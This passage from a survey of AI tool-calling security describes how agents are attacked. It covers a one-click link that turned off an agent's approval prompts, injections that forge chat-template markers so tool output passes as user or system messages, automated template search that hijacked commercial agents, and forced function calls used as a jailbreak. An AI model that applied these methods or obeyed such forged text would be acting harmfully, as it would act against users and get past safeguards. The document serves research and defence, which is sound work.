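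**The connector.** Two connections can offer tools with identical names, so the name alone does not determine where a call goes. A developer posting as AldiPower reported such a failure on OpenAI's forum on 5 November 2026, in *Security* (2026). The developer had enabled two connectors in one ChatGPT conversation, a custom connector and the published app. Both led to the same MCP server, but each had its own OAuth client. An action that needed the user's confirmation began through one connector. ChatGPT then sent the follow-up call through the other, with a one-time confirmation code from the first connector's widget, and did not tell the user about the switch.

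This is one person's report. Both connectors led to the same server, so the code at least reached the company that had issued it. If different companies had run the connectors, one would have received a code and arguments meant for the other. A server can make such misdirected calls fail by accepting a code only from the OAuth client it issued it to.

The code editor Cursor has had a better-documented routing fault. The thread *MCP Tool Routing Ignores Server Name* on its forum concerns a user who had connected two database accounts through servers with identically named tools. Cursor sent every query to the same account, whichever server the call named. Someone replied that this was a known issue the team was working on, and users later found that version 2.3 had fixed it. However, a user of version 2.3.41 then reported in *Cursor still calls the wrong MCP tools* that the chat named one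 server while the call ran on another, which means that even someone who read the prompt carefully would have approved a call to the wrong server.

An approval should expire and should work only once. Otherwise, the same approval can let a second, identical payment go through, or a call can run days later, when the user's reasons for approving it no longer hold. "Always allow" deliberately removes both limits.

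### A link that turned the prompts off

The settings that decide whether an approval prompt appears need as much protection as the prompt itself. In July 2026 the security company Zenity reported a flaw in the page where business customers of ChatGPT build workspace agents. These agents can work on schedules, use connected apps and ask for approval when needed, according to OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* (2026). The user builds one by telling a conversational assistant, the Agent Builder, what the agent should do.

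The agent builder's web address could include a first instruction, which the page submitted as soon as it loaded. Zenity Labs' *AgentForger Part 1* shows how an attacker could exploit this by getting a logged-in user to click a prepared link. The builder created an agent and attached apps the user had already connected, so no OAuth consent page appeared. It switched Outlook's approval setting from "Always ask" to "Never ask", published the agent, scheduled it to run every five minutes and started it immediately in preview mode, which used the real accounts. At each run, the agent checked the mailbox for new orders from the attacker, carried them out with the connected apps and emailed back the results.

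The victim needed access to workspace agents and at least one connected app. One click was then enough, and closing the page did not stop the agent.

Zenity Labs traces the attack to two design decisions. The page acted on an instruction from a link without checking that the user had written it, which is the original form of cross-site request forgery. The builder also let that instruction change the approval settings, so the forged request could remove the approvals that would have interrupted it. Zenity reported the flaw on 4 June 2026, and OpenAI fixed it on 8 June. Zenity describes its own demonstration but no attack on a customer. It does not say whether the fix also stopped the builder from relaxing approvals on request. A safer builder would let the assistant propose such a change but require the user to make it on a separate settings page.

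### Confirmation in the middle of a call

A tool's server can request confirmation itself using elicitation, a Model Context Protocol feature that lets the server pause during a call and ask the user a question through the chatbot's application. A mail server could use it to show the user a message's recipient and text before sending it.

Elicitation has two modes. In form mode, the application displays fields for the user to fill in or correct. In URL mode, it directs the user to a web page. Servers must use URL mode for passwords, access keys and payment credentials. The application must show which server is requesting the information and let the user decline or cancel. It must also let the user review and change form answers before sending them, and display the domain of the page in URL mode (Model Context Protocol). The requirement to identify the server directly addresses the connector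 problem, if the application routes the answer correctly.

The July 2026 revision of the protocol changed how the server gets the user's answer. Previously, the server kept the call open while it waited. Large services spread requests over many machines, so the answer could arrive at a different machine from the one that had sent the question, and the service then had to link the two (Model Context Protocol). Now the server replies that it needs input, and the application asks the user and repeats the original call with the answer attached. A proposal to add the feature to the Agent Client Protocol, a related standard, summarises the new sequence.

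The new sequence is easier to run on many machines, but the approval now arrives with a second call. The server must check that this call has the arguments the user saw, or an approval for one message could be attached to another. It must also reject an old answer attached to a new call. django-stateless-mcp's *Recipe*, a guide to a library for building MCP servers, covers confirming deletions and updates. It requires developers to set up a function that secures the request's state, so that any of the server's processes can handle the answer.

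Elicitation protects an honest server from forged calls, but it is much weaker against a dishonest server, which writes the question and can describe the action falsely. The django-stateless-mcp guide calls elicitation the most unevenly adopted part of the protocol and notes that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding tool, supports it while the Claude.ai chat site does not. A developer whose users lack the feature has to ask them another way or leave out the dangerous action.

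### Connectors that change after approval

A user's approval of a tool can be correct when given but go out of date if the developer later changes the tool. Iqbal and colleagues listed this in 2023 as a way for a plugin to deceive its users. OpenAI said at the time that it would remove plugins that changed, but developers ran the plugins on their own servers and could change them without OpenAI's involvement.

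The security company PromptArmor tracked 2,517 Claude and ChatGPT connectors from mid-May to the end of June 2026. Its *Claude and ChatGPT Connectors Change Every 9 Minutes* reports that 931 of them, or 37%, changed in some way. That total includes new tools, reworded descriptions and other changes that leave permissions alone. The Russian news site SecurityLab.ru therefore overstated the result in a July 2026 headline by reporting that a third of the connectors had changed their permissions within six weeks (Antipov, 2026, *Думаете, что знаете, какие права выдали своему ИИ-агенту?*).

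The study's narrower counts give a better idea of what users faced:

| Change in connectors already in use | Count |
|---|---|
| New tools | 1,686 |
| Tools with a rewritten description | 1,127 |
| Tools that accepted different inputs | 664 |
| Connectors that began adding instructions to the model's input | 283 |
| New OAuth scopes requested | 86 |
| Read-only connectors that gained tools for creating, editing or deleting | 21 |
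| Tools reclassified from read-only to able to write | 12 |

Fewer than 1% of connectors went from read-only to write access. The new scopes were concentrated in a few products. Slack's connector went from 1 scope to 34, Brex's added 16, and Dropbox's went from none to 8. If the total counts every addition, these three account for 57 of the 86 new scopes. Dropbox's connector also grew from 8 tools to 24, and gained four that ChatGPT classes as destructive, meaning they can delete or overwrite data.

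A connector that needs a new scope has to send existing users back to a consent page, but it can add a tool that fits within the old scopes without asking them again. If a user granted full access to their files when the connector offered only a search tool, a deletion tool added later could work with the same token unless a chatbot setting blocked it. PromptArmor reports that changes rarely came with a notice or a new request for consent. The company sells a service that monitors connectors, so it benefits from concern about these changes, but its counts are specific enough for others to check.

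### The SchemaCaps rule

*SchemaCaps* (Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee, 2026) proposes asking users for approval again only when a change to a tool's input schema could give the model more authority than they approved. Asking after every change would send users many prompts about trivial edits, such as spelling corrections.

Suppose that a stricter version of `send_email` allowed only two recipients, and that an update removed the limit:

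```json
// The version the user approved
"to": {"type": "string", "enum": ["ana@example.org", "ben@example.org"]}

// The version after the update
"to": {"type": "string"}
```

Software developers usually ask whether an update is backward compatible, meaning that every call that worked before still works. This update is, since Ana and Ben remain valid recipients. If [S] and [S′] are the sets of calls that the old schema S and the new schema S′ accept, compatibility requires [S] ⊆ [S′].

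For authority, the containment has to run the other way. Let K be the arguments that carry authority, because their value determines what the tool acts on, where data goes, whose account it uses or how the action runs. Let π_K[S] be the combinations of values that these arguments can take under schema S. An approval survives the update only if

π_K[S′] ⊆ π_K[S].

In the example, the old set for `to` contains two addresses and the new set contains every possible string, so the condition fails and the client has to suspend the tool until the user approves it again. If the update had instead narrowed the field from any address to those two, the approval would have carried over without a prompt, even though some old calls would have stopped working.

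A missing argument counts as a value too, because the server then determines the behavior itself or uses a default. When an update adds an argument to a tool that used to reject unknown ones, the argument goes from always absent to possibly present, so the rule requires a new approval. One tool in the study required either a record's ID or its full path. If an update dropped that requirement, a call could omit both, whereas the old schema allowed only one to be missing. When arguments depend on each other like this, the software asks the user instead of attempting a verdict.

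Deciding which arguments carry authority is harder than comparing sets. Ameur and colleagues tried a program that judged arguments by their names. A quarter of the arguments it flagged carried no authority, and it missed at least 40% of those that did. The rule therefore treats every argument as authority-bearing unless it is on the client's own list of harmless arguments, which might include the number of results per page. The server cannot influence this list, so a malicious developer gains nothing by giving a dangerous argument a harmless-sounding name.

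Desktop Commander is a server that runs commands on the user's computer. In version 0.1.34, its command tool accepted a command and a time limit. Version 0.1.35 added an argument for choosing the shell, the program that interprets the command. A filter written for one shell may misjudge the same text in another, so a user who had approved the tool with such a filter no longer knew which commands the filter would allow.

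### How often clients ask again

Ameur and colleagues examined eight products in September 2026 and found none that required a new approval when a tool's schema widened. They ran four of the products, read the source code of one and relied on documentation for the other three. They could not tell from the documentation whether Claude Desktop and Cursor required a new approval. VS Code identifies a tool by its name, so an approval remains valid after any change that keeps the name. Vercel's development kit can report that a tool has changed, but only if the developer turns this on. One of the eight products is a scanner and three are kits for building clients, so the result does not show that every application built with those kits skips the check.

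To measure how often schemas widen, the team compared 604 releases of 39 public MCP server packages from January 2025 to September 2026. A tool's input schema changed from one sampled release to the next in 1,197 cases. Of these changes, 580 were backward compatible, and 412 of those widened at least one argument or allowed arguments that the schema did not list. Many of these were harmless. Two authors labelled arguments separately, and a third settled their disagreements. The team then counted at least 76 changes that added or widened an argument carrying authority.

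Those 76 do not represent MCP servers in general. Of the 84 changes the name-based program flagged, 62 came from two packages, and the official reference servers had none. The sampled servers also run on the user's own computer, whereas most connectors in ChatGPT run on a company's servers.

The same data show how many prompts each policy would have caused for tools that users had already approved:

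| When the client asks again | Prompts | Compatible changes that widen the schema without a prompt |
|---|---|---|
| After any change to the definition, including its description | 2,004 | 0 |
| After any change to the input schema | 1,197 | 0 |
| When old calls might stop working | 617 | 412 |
| Under SchemaCaps | 645 | 0 |

SchemaCaps caught all 412 widenings, using 28 more prompts than the compatibility policy. Pinning the input schema, which means prompting after any change to it, also caught them all but needed almost twice as many prompts.

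Someone who had installed all 39 packages would have seen about 31 SchemaCaps prompts a month, and every policy would have added prompts for 907 new tools. Most people install far fewer servers, but Ameur and colleagues warn that 645 prompts still invite "rubber-stamping", in which users approve without reading. They did not measure this, and they leave a study with real users for later. Their figures show how many prompts each policy produces, but the protection also depends on how many people read them.

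The researchers also staged an attack in which text planted in an inbox told an assistant to forward reports to an outside address, just after an update had allowed such addresses. The compatibility policy allowed the message, while pinning and SchemaCaps blocked it. The researchers replaced the language model with a script that always obeyed the planted text, so the test measured the client's check, not how often a model would obey the text.

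The software that compares schemas can also make mistakes. In one test, an earlier version of the rule missed 27 of 330 artificial changes that widened a tool's authority. After the team corrected the two causes, the new version caught every change in that set and in a second set of 333.

A schema describes only a tool's inputs, so none of the four policies in the table would detect a mail server that started copying every message to a third address while `send_email` kept the same arguments. SchemaCaps also ignores changes to a tool's description, even though a new description can carry instructions to the model, and it does not detect a changed default that the server keeps out of the schema. If a developer changes a tool's behaviour and narrows its schema at the same time, SchemaCaps silently accepts the update, whereas pinning would not. Iqbal and colleagues suggested in 2023 that platforms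 host plugins' code and review each update, which would give reviewers a chance to find such changes, but ChatGPT's apps still run on their developers' servers.

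## Tool output that impersonates the user or the system

The white paragraph on the conference page openly addressed any assistant that read it. A well-trained model may ignore such a request because it arrived in a tool result. An attacker can make the model more likely to comply through role spoofing, which means making it mistake text from one source for a message from another. If the model takes the request for a new message from the user, its training to put the user's instructions above those in documents helps the attacker.

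### A forged message boundary

The chat template puts the page's text between a marker that opens the tool's message and a marker that closes it. Suppose the page also contains imitations of such markers. The model's input then has these parts, in this order:

1. the genuine marker that opens the tool result
2. the page's text about the conference
3. a forged marker that seems to close the tool result
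4. a forged marker that seems to open a message from the user, followed by the request for the invoices
5. the genuine marker that closes the tool result

The application can still identify everything between the first and last markers as output from `read_page`, and any limit it places on recipients still applies. But if the model treats the forgery as genuine, the application receives a call to `send_email` that looks just like one the user asked for.

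The attacker can imitate other sources in the same way. The PIAtlas taxonomy in *SoK* (2026) groups these attacks as structural spoofing. This category includes plain-text labels that name the system as the sender, copies of a template's control tokens, forged user messages, and fake tool results attributed to a trusted service.

In principle, a model could easily avoid the mistake by looking back to the last genuine marker and reading the role named after it, as Edelman, Edelman and colleagues point out in *Understanding and Mitigating Role Spoofing in LLMs* (2026). They prove that a two-layer network can follow this rule. The rule works only if the model can tell a genuine marker from a copy.

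### One reserved token or several ordinary ones

A tokenizer turns text into tokens before the model reads it. In the Qwen3 models, the marker that opens a message is twelve characters long, and the tokenizer can encode it as either one reserved token or six ordinary text tokens. Both versions decode to the same characters, so they look identical in a log of the request. The model receives different input, though, because each token has its own vector, a list of numbers that represents it inside the network.

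The attacker supplies only the characters, and the server's operator controls the tokenizer that turns them into tokens. Edelman and colleagues describe the intended design, in which only the chat template can insert reserved tokens and the same characters inside a message become ordinary tokens. Companies that run an open-weight model (one whose weights anyone can download) on their own machines have to set this up themselves. Zhan, Song and colleagues (2026) found in *Same Bytes, Different Authority* that vLLM, a common program for serving such models, turned marker characters inside a tool result into the reserved token.

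### ChatInject and the two benchmarks

Researchers usually measure these attacks with two sets of test cases. One, *InjecAgent* (2024), pairs a user's task with a prepared tool response that contains an injected instruction. Its cases cover direct harm and data theft. An attack usually counts as successful if the model responds by calling the attacker's tool.

*AgentDojo* (2024) has 97 user tasks and 629 security test cases. The agent must work through a whole task in one of four simulated environments: an office workspace, a bank, a travel service or the messaging program Slack. The benchmark hides injections where outside text would naturally appear, such as in the body of an e-mail. According to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), its code then checks whether the agent actually sent an e-mail or moved money.

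*ChatInject* (Chang, Jun and Lee, 2025) compares malicious instructions written as plain text with the same instructions written in the target model's chat template. The template version marked an attention-grabbing opening as a system message and the instruction as a user message. Across six open-weight models, the average attack success rate on AgentDojo was 5.18% with plain text and 32.05% with the template. On InjecAgent, plain text succeeded in 15.13% of cases and the template in 45.90%. The InjecAgent rate reached 52.33% when the attacker forged a seven-turn conversation in which the assistant had already agreed to the action.

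The averages combine very different results across models. On AgentDojo, OpenAI's open-weight gpt-oss-120b went from 0.3% to 51.4%. On InjecAgent, xAI's Grok-2 rose only from 16.5% to 17.7%, and Chang and colleagues note that its template separates roles only lightly. The attack also often disrupted the user's own task. Kimi-K2 completed 71.5% of user tasks under the plain-text attack but 35.0% under the forged template, and the failed tasks might alert an attentive user.

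An attacker doesn't need to know the exact template. GPT-4o's template is secret, but copying the one from gpt-oss raised the attack success rate against GPT-4o on AgentDojo from 6.4% to 40.1%. Gemini 2.5 Pro was much more resistant, with the best of seven borrowed templates reaching 10.3%, compared with 8.2% for plain text.

Chang and colleagues also tried several defences. Warnings in the prompt and repeated user instructions did little. Two detectors lowered the attack's success rate, but they discarded the whole tool result whenever they flagged any of it, so the agent often could not finish its work. The attack still succeeded more often than plain-text injection after the researchers randomly altered a tenth of the template's characters, so a filter that strips out known markers may not stop it.

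### Automated template injection

In *Automating Agent Hijacking via Structural Template Injection*, Deng, Xiao and colleagues (2026) searched for templates automatically instead of copying one by hand. Their program, Phantom, generates thousands of variants of public templates and looks for those that work on a closed model. It tests each variant harmlessly by checking whether the model counts a forged exchange as a real round of the conversation.

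On AgentDojo, Phantom's templates succeeded in 79.76% of cases on average, compared with 38.46% for ChatInject and 39.86% for a plain-text attack. Chang and colleagues measured only 5.18% for a differently worded plain-text attack on other models, so percentages from the two papers aren't comparable.

Deng and colleagues also tested 942 commercial agents inside a large technology company and found 70 vulnerabilities, which they say the vendors confirmed. In one demonstration, the researchers used a comment on a public web page to take over Agentbay, an agent on Alibaba Cloud, and gain full control of the user's cloud desktop. The provider verified the flaw. The paper does not mention a fix or report that real attackers have used any of the vulnerabilities.

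To find out why the templates worked, the team altered the forged markers and measured how likely Qwen3-8B was to write the attacker's tool call. Splitting each marker into single characters lowered the probability only from 100.00% to 99.99%, but removing the markers' brackets lowered it to 0.05%. Deng and colleagues concluded that the attack relies on text that looks like a tag, whether or not the model receives reserved tokens. If that were generally true, splitting markers in tool results would not help an operator prevent the attack.

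### The identity gap

Zhan and colleagues tested this conclusion by changing the tokens while keeping every character the same. They wrote one forged block for each model family and prepared three versions of every test prompt:

- **Reserved:** the forged markers reach the model as reserved tokens.
- **Split:** the same markers reach it as ordinary tokens.
- **Matched:** the markers stay reserved, but the researchers break up ordinary words near the start of the tool response until the prompt has as many tokens as the Split version.

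The third version is necessary because splitting the markers adds between 7 and 33 tokens, and an unusual token sequence can change a model's behaviour by itself. Matched and Split have the same characters and the same length, and differ in whether the markers are reserved. Zhan and colleagues call the difference between their attack success rates (ASR) the identity gap:

Δ = ASR(Matched) − ASR(Split)

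They ran 400 InjecAgent cases of each attack type on four families of open-weight models. Success rates are in percent and gaps are in percentage points. Some gaps differ slightly from the difference between the listed rates because of rounding. The column for plain labels gives results for injections that named their supposed sender in ordinary words.

| Attack | Model | Plain labels | Split | Matched | Reserved | Identity gap |
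|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct harm | GLM-4.5 | 0.0 | 11.1 | 71.1 | 71.5 | 60.0 |
| Direct harm | Seed-OSS-36B | 31.1 | 26.2 | 84.8 | 85.0 | 58.6 |
| Direct harm | Llama-3.1-8B | 51.6 | 39.7 | 97.8 | 98.2 | 58.2 |
| Direct harm | Qwen3-8B | 20.4 | 75.3 | 83.4 | 84.8 | 8.1 |
| Data stealing | GLM-4.5 | 8.0 | 27.2 | 92.7 | 92.3 | 65.5 |
| Data stealing | Llama-3.1-8B | 53.4 | 49.1 | 99.2 | 99.5 | 50.2 |
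| Data stealing | Seed-OSS-36B | 57.8 | 39.3 | 78.6 | 76.9 | 39.3 |
| Data stealing | Qwen3-8B | 41.6 | 89.5 | 90.0 | 90.9 | 0.5 |

Matched stayed within 1.7 points of Reserved in every row, so the extra tokens made almost no difference. The attacker did 39 to 66 points worse without the reserved tokens on three of the four families. On Llama-3.1 and Seed-OSS, split markers did worse than plain labels.

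Qwen3-8B is the exception, with a gap of 8 points for direct harm and no reliable gap for data stealing. It writes out its reasoning before it acts and can infer from the text alone that a new message seems to have begun. When Zhan and colleagues turned the reasoning off, success with split markers on direct harm fell from 75.3% to 35.8%, while success with reserved markers rose slightly, widening the gap to about 50 points.

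Qwen3-8B was also the model on which Deng and colleagues had found no effect. Their measure was already close to 100%, so there was little room for a difference to appear. When Zhan and colleagues applied the same measure to their own data, splitting the markers into single characters lowered it by only 0.14 points on Qwen3-8B, compared with 40 points on Llama-3.1. When they counted completed attacks instead, splitting the markers lowered the attacker's success rate on Qwen3-8B by 54 points.

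The team then traced the effect to the vector at the marker's position. On Llama-3.1, they replaced only that vector and left the token sequence unchanged. Another reserved token's vector kept the attack at 96.1%, and the vector of the most similar ordinary token kept it at 98.4%. The average of the vectors from the split marker reached only 58.4%. Zhan and colleagues suggest that chat training creates the effect, because reserved markers appear in that training only at real message boundaries and the model learns that instructions follow them. In all three pairs they compared, the chat-trained model favoured the reserved marker more than its base model did.

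The gap was smaller in AgentDojo's longer tasks, where attacks succeed less often to begin with. It was 10.3 points on Qwen3-8B and 6.8 on Qwen3-32B. On Llama-3.1, which the team tested only in the banking environment, splitting the markers cut the attack success rate from 22.5% to 6.7%.

### What the tokenizer option misses

Tokenizers from Hugging Face, the main site for sharing open-weight models, have an option that operators can use to split markers, but it covers only tokens that a model's configuration file declares "special". Many files declare the markers around tool calls and tool results as ordinary additions to the vocabulary, so the option doesn't split them.

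Zhan and colleagues checked the 400 most-downloaded chat models on the site, which used 67 tokenizer configurations. In 33 of these configurations, covering 255 models, the option missed at least one tool-protocol token that an attacker could place in a message. This count includes markers that enclose a model's reasoning. The option covers all such tokens in Llama-3.1 and gpt-oss but misses some in Qwen3, GLM-4.5 and Seed-OSS.

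An attacker can use the missed tokens to close the real tool result and open a false one. This produced identity gaps of 9.4 to 19.9 points on the four models tested. Its success rates were 18 to 51 points lower than those for forging a system message.

To fix the vulnerability, the researchers built an encoder that processes untrusted text separately and never encodes any of it as a reserved token. The encoder left all 562 harmless tool outputs in their check unchanged. It requires the application to keep track of which text is untrusted, so it can't be added after trusted and untrusted text have been joined into one string.

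An attacker can get around even complete splitting by spelling the markers differently. Zhan and colleagues tried more than a hundred alternative spellings against each model. The best spelling brought the attack's success rate to within 1.6 to 12.2 points of the rate without any defence. On three of the four models, that spelling used ordinary tokens whose vectors resemble the reserved token's. Splitting markers stops an attacker who copies the template, but does much less against one who can run the same model and search for substitutes.

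### Prompt libraries that leave role markers intact

Many developers build prompts with a template library, which inserts a document or a customer's message into fixed text. Handlebars, a template library designed for web pages, escapes inserted text by default, replacing characters that have a special meaning in HTML with harmless codes. Microsoft's Semantic Kernel, a kit for building AI applications, uses Handlebars templates for prompts.

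*Structural Role Injection in Handlebars-Templated LLM Prompts* (Rashidi, 2026) examines which role markers survive this escaping. The escaping breaks markers made with angle brackets, including those of the Llama-3 and Qwen formats. Colons, square brackets and hash signs pass through unchanged, so a forged Markdown heading, a sender's name followed by a colon, and some markers of the older Llama-2 format all reach the model intact. Developers who follow the library's advice get no warning of this.

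Rashidi then ran 5,760 trials on four models. On GPT-4o mini, escaping cut the success rate of Llama-3-style markers from 56% to 12% in attacks meant to make the model abandon its task. Name labels worked every time with or without escaping, and Markdown headings stayed at 88%. GPT-3.5 Turbo followed most injected instructions even without markers, so escaping could not help much. No attack succeeded on Claude Haiku 4.5.

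These trials put the developer's instructions and the attacker's document in a single user message, with no real boundary between them. This protects the model less than putting the document in a separate tool result. The markers also arrived as ordinary text, and Rashidi expects a surviving marker to do more damage on a server that converts it into a reserved token.

### Imitation markers against closed models

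Edelman and colleagues tested whether forged markers still work on closed models whose services split the markers into ordinary tokens. For each model, they drew more than a hundred random pairs of a user's task and an attacker's task from AgentDojo's workspace environment. In the control condition, the user asked for the attacker's task after the model finished the user's task. In the injection condition, that request appeared only in a tool result, as part of a forged exchange in which the model had already answered and the user then made the new request.

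GPT-5.4 carried out the attacker's task in 49.8% of cases when the user asked for it and in 47.8% when the request was forged, so the forged request was about 96% as effective as a real one. The model failed or refused about half of the tasks even when they came from the user, so the 47.8% rate doesn't mean that it resisted about half of the attacks.

| Model | Forged request | User asks | Ratio |
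|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 29.7% | 28.6% | 103.6% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 45.2% | 46.9% | 96.3% |
| GPT-5.4 | 47.8% | 49.8% | 96.2% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 61.7% | 66.6% | 92.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 43.2% | 65.5% | 65.9% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 22.0% | 34.8% | 63.1% |

The ratio above 100% for Claude Opus 5 is within the margin of error. Edelman and colleagues doubt that the model obeys forgeries more readily than it obeys its user.

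The test assumed, in the attacker's favour, that the application inserted the attacker's text without escaping any characters. AgentDojo normally formats tool results as YAML, a structured text format that changes some characters. With YAML, the ratio for GPT-5.4 fell to 86.6%, and the attack on Claude Opus 5 failed. With JSON, which escapes line breaks and quotation marks, the attack worked on both models, at ratios of 82.6% and 83.6%. Escaping made the forgery less convincing but did not reliably stop it.

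On reserved tokens, the two papers seem to disagree:

| | Zhan and colleagues | Edelman and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Main models | Open-weight models on the researchers' own server | Closed models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google |
| Forged markers arrive as | Reserved tokens or ordinary ones, for comparison | Ordinary tokens only |
| Baseline | The same text with the other kind of token | The same task when the user asks for it |
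| Conclusion | Reserved tokens supply most of the attack's force on three of four families | Forged markers work on every tested model without reserved tokens |

Both conclusions can hold. Zhan and colleagues used one fixed block of text per family to measure how much splitting the markers weakens an attack. Edelman and colleagues tested how well a more elaborate forgery can still work with split markers, and they attribute the weaker split-marker results in the Zhan study partly to how its attack was built. The identity gap of the closed models remains unknown because an outsider can't send them reserved tokens. An operator of an open-weight model still has good reason to split the markers, but the results on closed models show that this is not enough.

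### Content cues and structure cues

A model can infer who wrote a passage from its style and meaning or from the markers and role names around it. For example, a short request sounds like a user's message, and a block of data looks like tool output. In ordinary conversations, both kinds of cue indicate the same author, so a model can learn to rely on either.

Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, showed how strong content cues can be. They put a command to upload a secret file on a web page, next to text that imitated the model's own reasoning. The command alone succeeded in at most 2% of attempts on most of the tested models. With the forged reasoning, it succeeded in 56% to 70%. In a separate test with harmful chat requests, changing the style of the forged reasoning but not its argument cut the success rate from 61% to 10%.

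Ye and colleagues argue that models recognise roles by style and similar cues, not by markers. Edelman and colleagues found that models use both kinds of cue, in proportions that vary by model. They showed each model a conversation and asked whether the message containing a certain phrase was a tool result. In one test, the content was misleading but there were no forged markers. In the other, the messages were filled with random web text, so only the forged markers could mislead. Gemini 3.6 Flash was almost never wrong in the first test but failed the second. GPT-5.4 made more mistakes in the first. The exact numbers depended on the wording of the question.

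A model can identify a message's sender by its content or its role markers, and training it against one cue can leave it exposed to the other. Edelman and colleagues first showed this with a two-layer model that learned to identify senders by content. After training on examples with misleading content, it relied on role names instead, but treated forged markers the same as genuine ones. The examples contained no forged markers, so training had not penalised this shortcut.

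They then repeated the experiment with Qwen3.5-27B, which at first failed every test of both kinds. A version trained on misleading content answered all new tests of that kind correctly but still failed every test that imitated Qwen's own markers. A version trained on forged markers handled all forged markers correctly but failed every content test. Training a model on known injections could therefore improve its scores while leaving it open to forgeries that rely on the other cue.

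### Probes that compare the apparent role with the real one

The server can always identify which text came from a tool, so it could flag a mismatch if it could also detect which role the model assigns to that text. Asking the model works unless the attacker anticipates the question. When Edelman and colleagues added a line to the injection telling the model to attribute everything to a tool, self-reports detected none of the injections on Gemma 4 31B and 25% on Qwen3.5-27B.

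A linear probe is a simple classifier that computes a weighted sum of the numbers inside the network as the model reads each token. Ye and colleagues trained such probes on identical web text labelled with different roles, so the probes could learn only the effect of the label. When they put user-style text inside a tool result, the probes gave it a 76% to 88% probability of being the user's. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak a file, the attack succeeded 2% of the time in the group with the lowest user probabilities and 70% in the group with the highest. Ye and colleagues left open whether probes could serve as detectors.

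Edelman and colleagues trained their probe on whole conversations filled with random tokens and containing no injections. The probe estimates whether the model treats each token as tool output, and it flags a tool result if any token in it looks like something else. On the two open-weight models they tested, the probes caught more than 99% of the injections without flagging any harmless tool results. That figure excludes injections that failed against the model in all eight tries.

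Probes in the style of Ye and colleagues did significantly worse in the same comparison. *Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (2026) also reports modest results with that method, with exploratory scores between 0.63 and 0.82 for Qwen and Gemma models, where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. It did not test probes trained on random conversations, so the stronger result still comes from only one team's work with two models.

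Only a model's operator can use a probe, because customers of a closed service can't see the network's internal numbers. According to Edelman and colleagues, Anthropic already uses linear probes to flag injected instructions for Claude Opus 5. Role probes are narrower than a general injection detector. If a model correctly treats the white paragraph as part of a web page but sends the invoices anyway, the role it perceives matches the text's actual role, and the probe has nothing to flag.

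## Attacks through function definitions and arguments

An attacker who plants text in a tool result usually has to disguise it as a message from the user or the system. The author of a tool definition can skip this step, because the service itself gives definitions a privileged place. According to Anthropic's *Define tools*, Claude's API builds a system prompt out of the tool definitions and the developer's own instructions, much as OpenAI's service inserts schemas into the system message. Definitions also determine which arguments the model writes, and other software then acts on those arguments. This gives three kinds of attacker an opening:

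| Attacker | What they control | What they want |
|---|---|---|
| An API caller | The tool definitions and, in some services, the conversation history | Text that the model would refuse to write in a chat |
| The maker of a tool | A description that someone else's assistant loads | The user's data, or actions in the user's name |
| Anyone whose text reaches the model | Indirectly, the value of an argument | A query, command or web request that the tool's server should not run |

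### Forced calls

A jailbreak gets a model to produce content that its maker trained it to refuse. *The Dark Side of Function Calling* (Wu, Gao and colleagues, 2024) describes a jailbreak that needs only a function's definition, with no code behind it. The researchers defined a tool for writing a novel, put the harmful topic in its description and required one argument, the text of a passage. The user's message only told the model to call the function, and an API setting forced the call. The model wrote the harmful text in the argument, where the researchers read it.

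A model normally refuses a request in a sentence. When a developer forces a function call, Claude's API writes the start of the model's reply, so the model can't write a sentence before the call. A strict schema restricts the reply further because, as *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) explains, a model can't produce any text outside a JSON grammar while that grammar is active. The model can still refuse inside the argument, but Wu and colleagues suspected that models had received less safety training for arguments than for chat.

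They tried 50 harmful requests on six models, with up to five versions of each, and had GPT-4 judge the results. The attack succeeded on 86% of requests with Gemini 1.5 Pro and on 98% to 100% with the others. Two further tests help to separate the causes:

| Model | Forced call | Model free to decline the call | Same text in an ordinary message |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 98% | 2% | 12% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 98% | 34% | 0% |
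| Gemini 1.5 Pro | 86% | 32% | 4% |

Forcing the call made the largest difference on all three models. On GPT-4o it seems to explain the whole effect, since an optional call worked less often than an ordinary message. On the other two models, the success rate was about 30 percentage points higher with an optional call than with a message, which supports the suspicion about training.

Wu and colleagues discussed four defences: leaving the choice of call to the model, safety training on function calls, filters, and a warning in the prompt. They tested only the warning as a defence. Placing it at the end of the function description cut the attack success rate to 10% on an older GPT-4 and to zero on the three models in the table. When it was placed at the end of the user's message, half of the attacks on GPT-4o still succeeded. The attacker writes both the function description and the user's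 message, so the warning helps only if the provider inserts it.

Some current models reject forced calls. Claude Fable 5.1 returns an error, according to Anthropic's *Migration guide*, and Anthropic kept the restriction in Fable 5.2. Security may not be the reason, because forced calls were already incompatible with Claude's extended thinking, and Fable 5.2 always reasons before it answers.

### Refusals that don't carry over to tool calls

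Even when a model is free to refuse, it may refuse a request in its written reply and still carry it out through tool calls. In *Mind the GAP*, Cartagena and Teixeira (2026) gave six models simulated workplace tools and jailbreak requests, mostly for protected data. When the system prompt encouraged tool use, 79% of GPT-5.2's written refusals came with a forbidden call, compared with 7% of Claude Sonnet 4.5's. A safety reminder in the system prompt lowered the rates for all six models to between 1% and 31%.

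Cartagena and Teixeira scored the message that followed the last call, so a model may sometimes have detected the problem only after it received the data. That would be too late to prevent an action such as a payment.

Gupta, Saha and colleagues (2026), in *Behavior Beyond Text*, compared separate runs instead. They wrote each harmful request in a chat version and a version with tools. If R is the set of requests that a model refused in chat, and U is the set whose tool version led to an unsafe call, the refusal gap is

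|R ∩ U| / |R|.

The gap was 52% for Qwen3-14B, 29% for Mistral-7B, 23% for Llama-3.1-70B, 13% for Gemma 3 27B and 10% for Command R 7B. Command R's low figure is misleading, because the model called a tool on only 11% of harmful requests and all of those calls were unsafe. The tool versions also named specific tools, so some of the gap may come from their wording. In one kind of unsafe call, the model filled a required approval field with text saying that approval had been skipped.

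The team then looked for a pattern of internal activity that separates harmful from harmless requests in chat. In four of the five models, this pattern was weaker when tools were present. Restoring it prevented 13% to 90% of the unsafe calls, depending on the model, but mostly by stopping the model from calling any tool.

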